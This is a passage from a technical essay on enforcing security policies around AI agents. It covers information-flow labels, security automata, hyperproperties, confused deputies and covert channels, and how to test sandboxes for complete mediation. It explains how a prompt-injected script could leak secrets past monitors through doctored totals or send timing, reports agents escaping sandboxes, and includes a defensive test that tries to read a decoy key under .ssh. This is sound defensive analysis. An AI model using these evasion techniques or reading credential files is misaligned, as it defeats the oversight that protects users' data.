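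CaMeL (Debenedetti et al., 2025) combines this method with a separation between planning and reading. According to Shi and colleagues, CaMeL uses the user's request to work out the steps of a task and how data will move, so untrusted data can't change the program's course. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) explains that CaMeL and a similar system, FIDES, protect the planning model by putting untrusted tool results into variables that the model can refer to but not read.

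An interpreter that works this way could handle the sales task as follows:

1. The planning model writes the script from the analyst's request. It never receives the rows of sales.csv.
2. When the script opens the file, the interpreter labels the contents with their source and permitted readers, here the analyst and the reporting service.
3. Each operation gives its result the combined restrictions of its inputs. The total therefore has the same permitted readers as the amounts.
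4. At `send_total`, the policy compares the recipient with the label and allows the call. If the script tried to email a row to anyone else, the policy would refuse.

The customer's remark stays in a variable, so it can't cause the planning model to add the attacker's lines. But the model can't read the column names from the first few rows, as it did in the original example, so someone has to supply them. Shi and colleagues say that CaMeL reduces an agent's usefulness and requires changes to its internal design.

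Labels can also describe whether an attacker could have influenced a value. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (2025) presents FIDES, which uses these *integrity* labels alongside confidentiality labels. The survey *From Agent Traces to Trust* (2026) points out that untrusted data can cause harm by influencing an action, even if its content never leaves. If the host marked all of sales.csv as untrusted, a strict integrity rule would block even the honest total. FIDES can label individual fields, so the host could trust the amounts, which come from the company's till, and distrust the customers' remarks.

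This precision is lost when a language model processes the data. An interpreter can track an addition from its inputs to its result, but nobody can reliably determine which parts of a prompt influenced a model's answer. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (2025) explains that the system must therefore give the output every label on the model's inputs. After a few steps, all the data has every label, and the policy must either block nearly all calls or ignore the labels. The sales script avoids this problem because no model handles the data between `open` and `send_total`.

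*Sightline* (2026) tries to remove the surplus labels by estimating which inputs actually flowed into each tool call. Its evaluation used 120 steps from AgentDojo runs in which a small model, Qwen3-8B, was under attack. With a FIDES-style integrity rule, none of the 34 attack calls got through. Sightline removed more surplus labels than most of the comparison methods and kept the necessary labels in almost all attack cases. The result is promising, but 34 calls are too few to rule out occasional failures. Even if 8 percent of attacks could pass, a sample that size would show none about one time in seventeen.

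Labels also don't show whether a script added correctly. A false total that encodes a customer's name gets the same label as the true total because both come from the same file. To prevent this, the host would have to compute the total itself with a function the model can't change.

### Separate stages in Sandlock

Sandlock offers a coarser separation that works with ordinary programs. A developer divides a task into stages, runs each in its own sandbox, and connects them with pipes, which carry one program's output to the next. For the sales task, the first stage could read sales.csv without network access and write the total to the pipe. The second could contact the reporting service but not open sales.csv.

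Neither stage has the combination of private data, untrusted content and a way to communicate that Willison calls the "lethal trifecta". The kernel enforces the division without tracking individual values, so the first stage can use NumPy or any other compiled library. CaMeL needs its own interpreter to track them.

However, the first stage can write anything to the pipe. If an attacker controls that stage, it can pass on the customers' names, and a second stage that doesn't check its input will send them. Wang and Zheng acknowledge that Sandlock limits what each stage can do but not what passes between them, and they regard checks on the origin of data as complementary. For the sales task, it would be simpler, and sufficient, for the developer to write the second stage herself and have it accept only a number, as `send_total` does. She is also responsible for dividing the task sensibly,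 because Sandlock enforces whatever division she chooses.

### Who writes the policy?

A developer can test a policy before anyone uses it but can't foresee every task. Users know what they want but may describe it loosely, and Shi and colleagues warn that an ambiguous request can lead to an overly broad policy. A language model can write a new policy for each task in seconds, but its errors are only partly predictable.

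Wang and colleagues had OpenAI's o1, a model from 2024, write AgentSpec rules from a few examples. The rules caught 87 percent of the risky code in test cases o1 had not been given. Some failures occurred because o1 copied the examples too closely. For instance, a rule against deleting critical settings files might protect only the files named in the examples.

In tests with a household robot, about 96 percent of the actions that the generated rules blocked were unsafe, but the rules caught only 71 percent of unsafe actions. Given a vague instruction to avoid dangerous pouring, o1 also wrote a rule that banned all pouring, including watering a plant. Its driving rules prevented violations in five of eight scenarios, while hand-written rules did so in all eight. A newer model would probably write better rules, but a host can't tell from valid syntax whether a rule protects the right files.

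*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* describes hand-written Progent policies as error-prone, but they reduced the attack success rate on ASB to zero, compared with 3.9 percent for generated policies. Most of the generated policies' failures involved attack tools whose names and descriptions closely resembled those of legitimate tools. Shi and colleagues doubt that even a person could tell them apart without knowing in advance which to trust. Unlike a model reading the tool descriptions, a company's developer often has that knowledge.

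Progent lets an organisation write fixed rules that take priority over the policy for a particular task, so a model can't restore a call that those rules forbid. The task's policy also can't block a call that a fixed rule explicitly allows. The organisation should therefore use fixed rules mainly to forbid calls and only sparingly to allow them.

NVIDIA recommends a similar order. The organisation first forbids access to critical files outside the project, with no user override. The agent may then read and write freely within the project, except for configuration files. It may also access a short list of specific exceptions elsewhere. Any other access needs case-by-case approval. The analyst's `.ssh` directory belongs in the first group, so that she can't expose the key by clicking "Allow" when she is tired.

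## Which security properties can hooks guarantee?

The company might want the sales script never to open the private key. A hook can guarantee this, whatever program the model writes. The company might also want the script's total always to reach the reporting service, but a hook can't guarantee that by refusing calls, because a refusal can't make a script finish its work. Finally, the company might want the message to reveal nothing about individual customers. A hook can't check this from the script's calls alone, since a script that leaks customer data and one that doesn't may make exactly the same calls.

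### Safety properties

In *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000), Schneider worked out which policies a monitor can enforce if it can only follow a program's steps and stop the program before a forbidden one. Reference monitors, firewalls and most other enforcement mechanisms in operating systems fit this description. Such a monitor has to decide from the steps so far, without information about what the program will do next or what it would have done with different data.

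Schneider derived three conditions from this. The monitor must judge each run by itself, without comparing it with other possible runs. It can't let a violation pass in the hope that a later step will make up for it, because the program might end before that step. And it must reject a bad run after a finite number of steps. A policy that meets these conditions is a *safety property*. Schneider takes the formal definition from the computer scientist Leslie Lamport. A set of runs Γ is a safety property if the following holds for every run σ:

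```text
σ ∉ Γ  ⇒  ∃i: ∀τ ∈ Ψ: σ[..i]τ ∉ Γ
```

- σ is one run of a program, written as a sequence of steps, which may be infinite.
- Γ is the set of runs that the policy allows, so σ ∉ Γ means that the run breaks the policy.
- ⇒ means "implies", ∃i means "there is a number i such that", and ∀τ means "for every τ".
- σ[..i] is the first i steps of the run.
- Ψ is the set of all possible sequences of steps, and τ is any one of them. σ[..i]τ is therefore the first i steps followed by any continuation at all.

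In words, if a run breaks the policy, it does so within a finite number of steps, and nothing it does afterwards can undo the violation. For example, if the policy forbids opening the private key and a script opens sales.csv, sends the total and then opens the key, *i* is 3 because the third step breaks the policy. A monitor can prevent the violation by stopping the script just before that step.

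"The total always reaches the reporting service" has no such *i*. However long the script has run without sending anything, it might still send the total at the next step. In Schneider's commercial example, once a customer has paid, a monitor can block everything the seller tries to do except deliver the service, but the seller can still do nothing.

The Python policy for sales.csv qualifies because its refusals depend only on the call, its arguments and the calls already carried out. Safety properties can also be combined. If a kernel rule protects the key and a proxy limits the destinations, the script has to satisfy both.

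Hooks still can't enforce some safety properties. If the analyst must have her total within ten seconds, a violation is detectable after ten seconds, but stopping the script can't prevent it because time keeps passing. Schneider points out that a limit counted in program steps would be enforceable, since a stopped program takes no more steps.

### An automaton for "no sending after reading a secret"

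Schneider describes enforceable policies as *security automata*. An automaton has a set of states, at least one of them a starting state, and rules that give the next state for each step. If no rule covers a step, the monitor stops the program. His first example forbids a program to send messages once it has read a file. A version that applies only to secret files needs two states:

| Current state | Script reads a secret file | Script sends data | Any other step |
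|---|---|---|---|
| No secret read (start) | Go to "secret read" | Stay | Stay |
| Secret read | Stay | No rule: stop the script | Stay |

Suppose that only the private key counts as secret, and that the script includes the attacker's two lines:

| Step the script attempts | State before the step | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Open sales.csv | No secret read | The script continues |
| Send the total to the reporting service | No secret read | The script continues |
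| Open the private key | No secret read | The script continues, in the state "secret read" |
| Send the key to the attacker's server | Secret read | The monitor stops the script |

This policy lets the script read the key, which helps if a task needs a secret for local work. But the protection depends on what counts as sending. A script could print the key for the model to read and then end. If the host starts a fresh automaton for the next script, the model can copy the key into that script, which begins in the state "no secret read" and can send it. The host should therefore keep one state for the whole session and apply it to the model's other tools.

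The monitor must also receive both file-read and request events. Landlock controls file access and an egress proxy handles requests, but neither can run this automaton alone. The proxy, for example, has no record of what the script read. A supervisor or a set of host functions can receive both kinds of event.

The monitor doesn't need to see every event. Schneider shows that a filter can hold back any step that would leave the monitor's state unchanged, which saves a lot of time. In the starting state, only reads of secret files have to reach the monitor. The host must then protect the filter too, because a script that corrupted it could hide a read of a secret file.

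If the company also declares sales.csv secret because it contains customers' names, the monitor stops the script at its second step, and the script never sends the legitimate total.

### Monitors that hold back or add actions

*Edit Automata* (Ligatti, Bauer and Walker, 2003) studies monitors with more powers. An *edit automaton* transforms a program's sequence of actions before they take effect. It can end the program, suppress an action while the program continues, or insert an action the program didn't request. It can change a call's argument by suppressing the call and inserting one with the new argument.

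Suppose the company's auditors require a log entry for every total it sends. This isn't a safety property. A script that has sent a total without an entry breaks the rule for the moment, but it can put that right by writing the entry next. A monitor that can only stop the script has no good choice when the script calls `send_total`. If it allows the call, the script may end before writing the entry. If it refuses, no total ever goes out. An edit automaton can hold the call back:

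| What the script does | What the monitor carries out |
|---|---|
| Calls `send_total(48210.5)` | Nothing yet |
| Then calls `write_log("June total")` | Both calls, in order |
| Or ends without writing an entry | Nothing, and it discards the total |

Edit automata can thus enforce some policies that aren't safety properties. (The theory assumes that the monitor keeps running, so a power cut between the two calls would still leave a total without an entry.) Sandlock does something similar when it holds a script's file changes until the host accepts them.

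The method works best when the script doesn't need an answer to the suppressed call. If the script waits for the reporting service's receipt before it writes the log entry, the monitor must either return a fake receipt or leave the script waiting.

Even an edit automaton can't guarantee that the total reaches the reporting service. It could repeat a failed request, but it can't make the service accept one. It also can't insert a total that the script never calculated unless the host can calculate it, which would make the script largely unnecessary.

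### Why secrecy is not a property of a single run

Revealing nothing about individual customers is difficult for a different reason. Suppose the amounts in the file add up to 48,210.50. An honest script sends that total. A hostile script calculates the same total but uses the last digit as a signal, replacing it with 1 if the first customer's name begins with a letter from A to M, and with 0 otherwise.

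| First customer | The honest script sends | The hostile script sends |
|---|---|---|
| Weber | 48210.50 | 48210.50 |
| Adler | 48210.50 | 48210.51 |

When the first customer is Weber, both scripts open the same file and send the same number. A hook that receives only these calls must give both scripts the same verdict. Yet an attacker who wrote the hostile script and can read the reporting service's records learns from the final 0 that the name begins with a letter from N to Z. The 0 is informative because the script would have sent a different number for Adler, and that number does not appear in the run.

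Clarkson and Schneider (2009), in *Hyperproperties*, therefore treat secrecy as a property of a program's whole set of runs. They call such a property a *hyperproperty*. One version, *observational determinism*, requires the following:

```text
∀t, t′ ∈ T:  t[0] =L t′[0]  ⇒  t ≈L t′
```

*T* is the set of all runs the program can produce, and *t* and *t′* are any two runs in it. *t*[0] is the state in which a run starts. =L means that an outsider, who has access only to public information, can't tell two states apart, and ≈L means the same for whole runs. So if two runs differ at the start only in their secrets, an outsider must not be able to tell them apart later. In the example, the names are secret and the amounts count as public, because the company intends to release their sum. The honest script meets this requirement, but the hostile script breaks it, as the two rows of the table together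 prove.

Two runs are enough to expose such a leak, so a host can test for one by running the script on the real file and on a copy with invented names, then sending the total only if both runs produce the same number. But if the invented name also begins with a letter from N to Z, the hostile script produces the same total twice and the test misses the leak. Clarkson and Schneider describe a technique called *self-composition* for proving that no pair of runs differs. It joins a program to a copy of itself with renamed variables, and the proof must show that equal public inputs always give equal public outputs. This turns secrecy into a safety property of the combined program, but proving it requires analyzing the program's code, which a hook doesn't do.

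Refusing some runs can create a leak. Clarkson and Schneider describe a system that unpredictably outputs 0, 1 or the value of a secret bit. Both outputs are possible whatever the secret is, so the set of possible outputs reveals nothing. If a monitor allowed only the runs that output the secret bit, those runs would disclose it. By contrast, refusing more runs never violates a safety property.

A check that consults secret data can also leak that data. Suppose the host function `send_report` refuses any report that contains a customer's name. A script with no access to the customer list can find out whether someone is a customer by submitting a report that contains only that person's name and checking whether the call returns an error.

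### Stricter rules that also stop harmless scripts

Schneider explains that monitors said to prevent information flow actually enforce a stricter policy, which guarantees secrecy but also forbids some runs that leak nothing. In the extreme case, a policy that refuses every run would keep every secret. The two-state automaton is also too strict when sales.csv counts as secret, since it stops the honest script as well as the hostile script that tries to send a doctored total.

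In practice, the company must decide which harmless scripts it can do without. The host could remove the names from sales.csv before the script gets it. The total then can't depend on the names, and the policy becomes a rule about which file the script may open, which a hook can enforce. The sales script would still work, but a script that counts distinct customers would not, even though its result might be harmless. CaMeL's data labels stop fewer harmless scripts, but they are also an approximation, because a result keeps the label of a secret even if the script multiplied the secret by zero.

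Alternatively, the host can limit how much information each message can carry. The Python policy for the sales task rounds totals to the cent and lets those below 100,000 go out without approval. There are ten million such totals, enough to encode nearly five letters of a name. The limit is a safety property, but if the host applies it to each run separately, an attacker can collect a few more letters every day.

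Clarkson and Schneider discuss a simple version of this problem, in which a system splits a secret into *k* shares and can output one share in each run, so that *k* runs together can reveal the secret although no single run does. A host can address this by keeping a count across scripts. The monitor then treats the whole series as one long run, and a limit on the total number of messages is again a safety property. The company has to choose the limit, and a report sent every day for years will need a high one.

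### What the guarantee depends on

Hooks can guarantee that no script does a particular harm if three conditions hold: mediation is complete, the script can't tamper with the monitor, and the policy forbids every sequence of steps that does that harm. The guarantee holds whether the model is honest, mistaken or under an attacker's control. It is much stronger than a low attack success rate in tests because it also covers attacks that nobody has tried. A more capable model can weaken it only by finding a way to break one of the conditions.

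For the sales task, such a guarantee covers some harms and not others:

| Unwanted result | What a hook can guarantee |
|---|---|
| The script opens the private key | It never happens |
| The script contacts an unlisted server | It never happens |
| The script sends two totals | It never happens, if the monitor counts across scripts |
| The script sends a wrong total | Only that the number is within the permitted range |
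| The total encodes part of a name | A limit on the number of letters, or none at all if the script can't read the names |
| The total never arrives | Nothing |

The policy is often the weakest of the three conditions. A rule against sending works only if its definition of "send" covers every way to send, because an attacker can use any that the developer forgot. According to Schneider, a program may have many ways to send, "some obvious and others buried deep within the bowels of the target".

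A policy can also forbid every harmful call its author anticipated and still allow harm, because a permitted call may serve the wrong purpose, as the doctored total does. Similarly, a coding agent with write access to a project can delete the line that checks a user's password, and the hook receives an ordinary edit. NVIDIA leaves inaccurate and manipulated output out of its sandboxing guidance and treats it as the user's responsibility.

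### The confused deputy

Sometimes a script gets a trusted program to do something the script itself is forbidden to do. In *The Confused Deputy*, Hardy tells a "nearly true" story from Tymshare, a company that rented out time on shared computers in the 1970s. Tymshare's compiler was in a system directory, and a user who ran it could name a file to receive debugging output.

*The Confused Deputy*, a set of lecture slides on the same case, describes what went wrong. The compiler also recorded each user's processor time in a billing file, which it could write to but ordinary users could not. A user named the billing file as the destination for the debugging output. The operating system checked that the compiler could write to that file and let it overwrite the billing records. The compiler had two sources of authority, its own and the user's, and nothing in the request showed which one it should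 use.

Host functions can fail in the same way. For example, a developer might supply `make_chart(data, path)`, which draws a chart on the host and saves it at the given path. The sandbox prevents the script from writing outside `charts/`, but the script can call `make_chart` with the path of the analyst's tax spreadsheet. The hook runs, and the policy allows the call because charts are part of the task. The operating system then allows the write because the host has permission to write there, and the host overwrites the spreadsheet.

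A stricter policy could check the path. Hardy's case convinced him that capabilities were necessary, and they prevent the confusion from arising. The script would pass `make_chart` an open handle for the output file instead of a name, and `make_chart` would write to that handle. A script that can't open the spreadsheet for writing has no such handle to pass. Java's stack inspection addressed the same problem by checking the caller's permissions along with the library's.

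The remedy is harder to apply when someone else owns the deputy, as with an outside reporting service that fetches pictures from any address it receives. The company can only limit which requests the script may send to the service.

### Covert channels

A *covert channel* carries information through something not intended for communication, such as when a program acts. The hostile sales script could send the true total, correct to the cent, but choose the second at which to send it. If the script and the recipient agree on a starting time, an hour gives 3,600 possible seconds, enough to encode two letters of a customer's name. The request's destination and content are correct, so even the strictest check on its body allows it.

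Monty's option to freeze the clock doesn't stop a script from leaking information through the time at which it sends a total. The script doesn't need a clock to delay sending with a loop, and the attacker can time that loop beforehand on his own machine. The host can prevent this leak by holding every total until the top of the hour, as long as the script finishes by then. That delay is acceptable for a monthly report but not for a program that exchanges messages with a server all day.

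A script can also leak information through whether its message arrives, for example by crashing on purpose if the first customer is Adler. Clarkson and Schneider note that their version of observational determinism permits such *termination channels*, because it compares two runs only up to the end of the shorter one. A single crash reveals at most one yes-or-no answer, but repeated runs reveal more, so the host should limit how often a failed script can retry.

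A company protecting customers' surnames might reasonably accept leaks of this size, but even a slow leak eventually reveals an entire private key. The safest policy for a key is to prevent the script from reading it, so that the script can't leak it through timing.

### Permitted writes that take effect later

A monitor can stop a script only while the script is running, but some harm happens afterwards. In OpenAI's example, malicious code planted in the Prettier formatter runs later, in the analyst's editor.

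The company can extend the monitoring to the editor. NVIDIA recommends sandboxing the whole development environment, including everything it starts, and where possible running it under a separate user account. When Prettier then runs the planted code, the code is under the same restrictions as the script that planted it. The editor also loses access, so the analyst may have trouble opening files from elsewhere on her machine.

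The other approach is to forbid the write. NVIDIA tells developers to block changes to configuration files wherever they are, because these files can define hooks or start tool servers that often run outside the sandbox. This rule is a safety property, because the forbidden write is visible in the script's own run. Like the stricter rules for secrecy, it stops some harmless work. Protecting Prettier's whole directory, for example, would stop the agent from installing or updating packages there.

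A list of protected files cannot cover ordinary source code, because a coding agent's task is to write programs that somebody will run. The company has to review the code before it runs with full access, or keep running it in a sandbox.

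## How can one tell that the hooks catch every privileged call?

Suppose the company demonstrates its sandbox to an auditor. The sales script sends its total, and the attempt to open the private key fails. This tests only one way to read the key. A child process, a native library or the agent's file-reading tool might still open it, and an attacker needs only one of them. Refused calls can't prove complete mediation, however many there are, because a single path without a hook is enough to disprove it.

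A gap in the hooks can matter even without an attacker. Anthropic reports that its Claude models have escaped a sandbox to complete a task, and that more capable models are better at finding "unexpected paths to a goal".

### Listing the paths

A tester first needs to know which paths exist. Son (2026), in *Governed MCP*, counted 59 in Anima OS, an experimental operating system whose kernel checks the tool calls of AI agents:

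| Kind of path | Number | What Son found |
|---|---|---|
| Host functions for WebAssembly programs | 18 | The kernel checks 15, and the other 3 only read |
| Registered tools | 20 | The kernel checks all of them |
| System calls | 21 | 8 have a check, 7 touch nothing that the policy protects, and 6 reach resources with no check |

An earlier version of the paper claimed that the kernel checked all 123 paths, but Son withdrew that claim. Agents that run as WebAssembly can't use the six gaps because they can't make system calls, but an ordinary program could. A tester who picked ten of the 59 paths at random would have had a 31 percent chance of missing all six gaps. If there had been only one gap, the chance of missing it would have been 83 percent.

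A list is more useful if the system refuses whatever isn't on it. *Sleeper Channels and Provenance Gates* (2026) describes a ten-hook design that denies any kind of action its specification doesn't name. A reviewer can then compare the program with a written list instead of trying to imagine every possible action. According to the paper, some operations still escape the hooks, such as calls to native code and data storage by browser plug-ins.

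### Testing in pairs

Each path needs two tests, one with a call that must succeed and one with a call that must fail. A refusal alone may have nothing to do with the sandbox. If the office network is down, a connection to the attacker's server fails whether or not a hook exists. A success alone is no better, because the sales script also runs perfectly well without a sandbox. For reading files, the tests might look like this:

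```python
import subprocess

ALLOWED = "/data/sales.csv"
DECOY = "/home/analyst/.ssh/decoy"     # contains only the marker
MARKER = "7f3c-decoy-91ab"

def direct(path):
    with open(path) as f:
        return f.read()

def child(path):
    return subprocess.run(["cat", path], capture_output=True, text=True).stdout

for read in (direct, child):
    assert "amount" in read(ALLOWED)
    try:
        text = read(DECOY)
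    except OSError:
        text = ""
    assert MARKER not in text
```

The test tries to read a decoy beside the real key, so it exposes nothing of value if the sandbox is broken. The tester must confirm from outside the sandbox that the decoy exists, because the test would also pass if the decoy were missing. A fuller version would add a function for each other way of reading the file, such as memory mapping, a native library and the agent's own file tool. For network calls, the forbidden address should belong to a server the company runs, so that the tester can check whether anything arrived.

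*Measuring the Energy Cost of Completing Tasks with Quantized Language-Model Agents* (2026) used a planted marker in a similar way. The agents could have cheated by finding the expected answers, so the researchers tried to read the answer files directly, through `..`, through symbolic links and through the parent process's environment variables. They also tried to write files, start processes and open connections. The sandbox had to refuse every attempt before the experiment could begin. Wang and Zheng's ten checks for Sandlock include some pairs too.

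Pairs can also show how several sets of rules combine. GitLab lets both administrators and projects list domains for its agents' sandbox. Flexible mode adds a project's permitted domains to the administrator's list, while strict mode ignores them. Both modes apply the project's forbidden domains. GitLab says these rules are easy to get wrong. One request to a domain that only the project permits would show which mode is on.

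### When the sandbox doesn't start

A test result applies only to the configuration in which the test ran. GitLab, for example, runs an agent by default even if its sandbox can't start. Before the agent starts, GitLab's job looks for the sandbox runtime's command, `srt`, writes its settings and tries to create a sandbox. If this fails, the job logs a warning that ends "running command directly without sandbox". The network rules then no longer apply, so the agent can contact any address the machine can reach.

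The agent may still finish its task, so the job looks like any other successful one. In GitLab's words, "A flow can run fine and still be unprotected." A test that passed last month in a different container image wouldn't reveal the problem.

The setting "Don't run flows when the sandbox is unavailable" makes such jobs fail instead, with an error message that includes "refusing to run because the sandbox is required". Individual projects can't turn the setting off, but a project with its own image can still supply a fake `srt`.

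A project's `setup_script` is another gap. According to GitLab, the script's commands run before the sandbox starts and can read the access tokens of the person who started the job. Anyone who can change that file can therefore run commands outside the sandbox with someone else's tokens. GitLab recommends that a security reviewer approve every change to the file. It also suggests restricting outgoing traffic with a firewall on the machine, which would still limit a job that runs without a sandbox.

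Another part of the same product fails closed. GitLab's *Agent tool governance* explains that an agent receives no tools if the service can't determine which rules apply. But GitLab didn't enforce these rules for agents running in automated jobs, according to its July 2026 help text, so the check never ran there and failing closed couldn't help.

A sandbox can also test itself each time it starts. In OpenParallax, which *Parallax* (2026) describes, the agent's process first tries to do four things that should fail:

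- write a file on the host
- read a known host file
- contact an unauthorised address
- access the process that supervises it

If any attempt succeeds, the system does not start, much as Deno ends the process when its broker fails. The probes are not paired with similar calls that should succeed, so the system can't tell a blocked attempt from one that failed for another reason. If only the network rule were missing and the network were down during the probes, all four attempts would fail, the system would start, and the agent would have open network access once the connection returned.

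### The 51 tests in SandboxEval

Writing tests for every path takes time, so a shared collection is useful. *SandboxEval* (Rabin, Hostetler and colleagues, 2025) provides 51 Python tests for Linux systems that run model-written code. Nineteen collect information about the system and its files, and 17 try to change files or their permissions. The other 15 try to communicate with the outside or cause damage, for example by filling the disk.

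The tests ran on Dyff, a platform for evaluating AI systems. Dyff runs untrusted code under gVisor, as an ordinary user, with nearly all network traffic blocked. Every attempt to communicate with the outside failed on Dyff, while the same attempts all succeeded on a researcher's laptop. The laptop runs served as a control, showing that the attempts could succeed when nothing blocked them.

The tests also found keys, network addresses and hashes in the environment variables of Dyff's container. The researchers then reviewed whether the container needed these variables. A log of system calls would probably not have shown this exposure.

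Some of the results are weaker than they appear. Rabin and colleagues recorded "Denied" for permission errors and whenever a test didn't return the expected result, so a missing program could look like a working sandbox. They also didn't carry out many of the dangerous actions. For file changes, they inferred the result from whether the user had write permission, but a hook may refuse a write that the file's permissions allow. They don't claim that the suite covers every attack, and it has no test for a check-to-use race.

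ControlPlane, a consultancy, offers Sandbox Probe for testing the sandboxes built into AI tools. SandboxEscapeBench, a 2026 benchmark, measures how well language models can escape sandboxes.

### A strength score from 0 to 4

Passing a test also doesn't show how hard a hook is to defeat. The Agent Sandbox Taxonomy, which appeared in March 2026, tries to score this. TechRadar's *The AI escape is a red herring*, an opinion piece by the chief executive of the software vendor Coder, describes how it works. The taxonomy divides a sandbox into seven layers: isolation from the host, resource limits, files, network, credentials, control of actions, and logging. Each layer gets a strength from 0 to 4, and a separate score from 0 to 3 for how finely its rules can distinguish cases. Protections for the sales script would score roughly as follows:

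| Strength | Meaning | Example |
|---|---|---|
| 0 | Nothing enforces the rule | A script running under the analyst's account |
| 1 | The script can ignore the rule | Environment variables that name a proxy |
| 2 | Software outside the script's control enforces the rule, but an operator can change it | An egress proxy that is the only way out |
| 3 | The kernel enforces the rule, and the process can't undo it | Landlock |
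| 4 | The protected resource doesn't exist inside the sandbox | A reporting key that the host adds to requests outside |

Under the taxonomy, data theft counts as addressed only if the file, network and credential layers all score at least 2. A score of 2 doesn't guarantee protection, since TechRadar's author estimates that the network boundary in the July 2026 incident would have scored 2. The project has scored 26 products, nearly all from their documentation, but it also supplies a probe for testing a running sandbox.

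These scores measure how strong a hook is, not how many paths have one. Landlock scores 3, but the private key is still exposed if the agent's file-reading tool runs outside the Landlock sandbox. The taxonomy recommends combining products and taking the highest score at each layer. To assess complete mediation, an assessor should calculate that combined score separately for each path and then use the lowest result, because the attacker will choose the weakest path.

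### Comparing two logs

A tester can find only the gaps she thinks to try. Logs from two different positions can expose others. Suppose the sales script runs in ordinary CPython, where it can use `send_total` or open its own connection. The host records every call to `send_total`, and all traffic, including the host's, passes through the company's proxy:

| Time | Log of host functions | Log of the proxy |
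|---|---|---|
| 09:00:01 | `send_total(48210.5)` | `POST /totals` to the reporting service |
| 09:00:04 | Nothing | A connection to a package site |

The second connection has no matching entry, so something reached the network without using the host function. The comparison reveals that path even if nobody suspected it in advance. Assay, a monitoring tool for coding agents, can supply one of the two logs. It runs the agent in a sandbox and records its file operations and the programs it starts, independently of the agent's own permission prompts. Son's tests of Anima OS similarly checked the tool calls they made against the kernel's own count.

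The entries rarely match one to one. A single `urlopen` causes many system calls, and Python opens dozens of files that aren't named in the script. The tester has to account for this routine activity before an unexplained entry is good evidence of a missed call. Both logs also cover only what programs did during the recording, so a path that no program took appears in neither.

*ZeroGate* (2026) discusses a trial mode that logs what a policy would have decided but lets every call continue. Such a trial can reveal a missing hook, but it can't show that the policy would stop any calls. Before relying on enforcement, the company has to test it on retries, other credentials, direct calls to a service's library, child processes and background tasks. *ZeroGate* acknowledges that its own research version doesn't achieve complete mediation against an attacker who holds an access token.

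### The Brown University system

*Static analysis* examines a program's code without running it and reports everything the code might do. It can find a call in a rarely used branch that no test has run and no log has recorded. *Towards Practically-Secure Tools for AI Agents* (Adam, Lu and colleagues, 2026) applies it to tool servers, the programs that offer tools to a model. A model chooses a tool by its description, which may be incomplete. In the paper's example, a tool's description mentions only writing a file, but the tool also sends the length of the text to a metrics service.

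The Brown system works as follows:

1. The researchers label library functions that affect the outside world, such as those that write files or send data. They call these actions *effects*.
2. An analyser starts where the model's request enters a tool and follows the data through the code to every labelled function it might reach. The design requires the analyser to reject direct system calls or treat them as very broad effects, so that a tool can't avoid the labels that way.
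3. The analyser produces a summary, the *synopsis*. For the example, it reports that the text may go to a file and to the network.
4. The developer replaces each plain file write with a call to a wrapper. The wrapper receives the path and the rules for that particular request, and refuses a write that breaks them.
5. A second pass through the code verifies that no effect lacks a wrapper, and that nothing in the tool can alter the rules before they reach it.
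6. When the model requests the tool, a program on the user's side compares the synopsis with the user's policy. It either blocks the request or sends it on with rules for the wrappers.

Each wrapper is a hook, and step 5 checks for complete mediation, meaning that every privileged call goes through a hook. The wrappers are necessary because the analyser can't determine which path the model will supply. Without them, the analyser would have to report that the tool might write anywhere, and a policy that permits writes only to the project's folder would block every write.

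Adam and colleagues tried the system on an existing Rust tool server for programmers. The analysis showed that the server's own file-writing tool had no limit on where it could write. It also found a hidden network call that the researchers had planted. Another tool, which only produced a plan, had no effects and needed no wrapper.

The researchers then compared four kinds of protection on three tasks, each with a harmless version and a harmful one. In the harmful versions, the model saved an access key in the wrong folder, the tool sent metrics while the user worked on confidential code, or the agent published a project that contained a key. They replayed recorded sessions so every protection received the same requests.

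| Protection | Harmless versions it allowed | Harmful versions it blocked |
|---|---|---|
| None | 3 of 3 | 0 of 3 |
| One fixed sandbox around the server | 2 of 3 | 1 of 3 |
| Static analysis without wrappers | 2 of 3 | 3 of 3 |
| Static analysis with wrappers | 3 of 3 | 3 of 3 |

The fixed sandbox blocked a user-requested change to a shell start-up file. Static analysis, used alone, blocked the same task because it couldn't rule out writes to other folders.

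The six cases show that the design can work, but they give little evidence of how often it would miss a real problem. The researchers chose the cases, and the prototype relied on being given the right policy for each request. Rust also makes this kind of analysis easier. Many tool servers use Python or JavaScript, where reliable analysis is much harder and would probably reject more harmless calls.

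The analysis also can't follow data out of the tool's own language into a shell command, a database or a web service. The prototype therefore runs shell commands in a temporary view of the file system and sends their network traffic through a proxy. If the server runs on someone else's machine, the user also needs evidence that it is running the code the analyser examined. A complete system would get this from *remote attestation*, in which hardware certifies which program is running.

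For the sales task, this method would suit the host functions, because the developer writes their code in advance. It could confirm, for instance, that `make_chart` writes files only through its wrapper. It suits the code-execution tool less well, because a synopsis made before the model writes the script would have to list every possible effect. The tool would still need hooks around the running script to catch its privileged calls.

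### What a proof assumes

A formal proof can cover every program that an agent might submit. *Proof-Carrying Contracts* (2026) proves that certain commitments hold even against a hostile agent. The proof assumes *isolation*, meaning that the agent can act only through the mechanism that checks its actions. If the agent could bypass that mechanism, for example by deleting messages from a mailbox while a tool was reading it, the proof would no longer apply.

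A company that wants to rely on such a proof must therefore establish isolation on its own machines, again by listing the paths, testing them in pairs, and looking for unexplained entries in the logs. For conclusions about the world outside the program, the system's records must also match reality. If a payment ledger is wrong, for example, a proof about the ledger doesn't establish anything about the money itself.

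### Reported failures by missing requirement

Failures in earlier sandboxes show which kind of check would have been useful:

| Missing requirement | Reported failure | A check that could expose it |
|---|---|---|
| A hook covers every path | Deno let a script get a file's status through an open handle | A forbidden call for every operation, not just for opening files |
| The sandbox runs, or the job stops | GitLab's default lets an agent run unprotected | A forbidden call in each job before the agent starts |
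| The script can't change the hook or its rules | Pirch and colleagues manipulated IronClaw's configuration | An attempt to edit the settings from inside the sandbox |
| The kernel uses what the hook checked | Watson's attacks changed arguments after the check | Tests in which a second thread changes the arguments |
| People can verify the hook | Janus kept wrong records of socket protocols for years | A comparison with the kernel's own records |

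The sandbox's settings file needs checking whenever a developer lets an agent write to more places. GitLab's *Allow /tmp writes in the SRT sandbox for Duo Workflow* describes opening `/tmp` to models, which naturally use it for scratch files, and moving the sandbox's settings to a separate directory that the agent can't change.

Developers continue to find and repair flaws in current products. OpenAI, for example, fixed flaws in Codex in 2026 after receiving reports of them.

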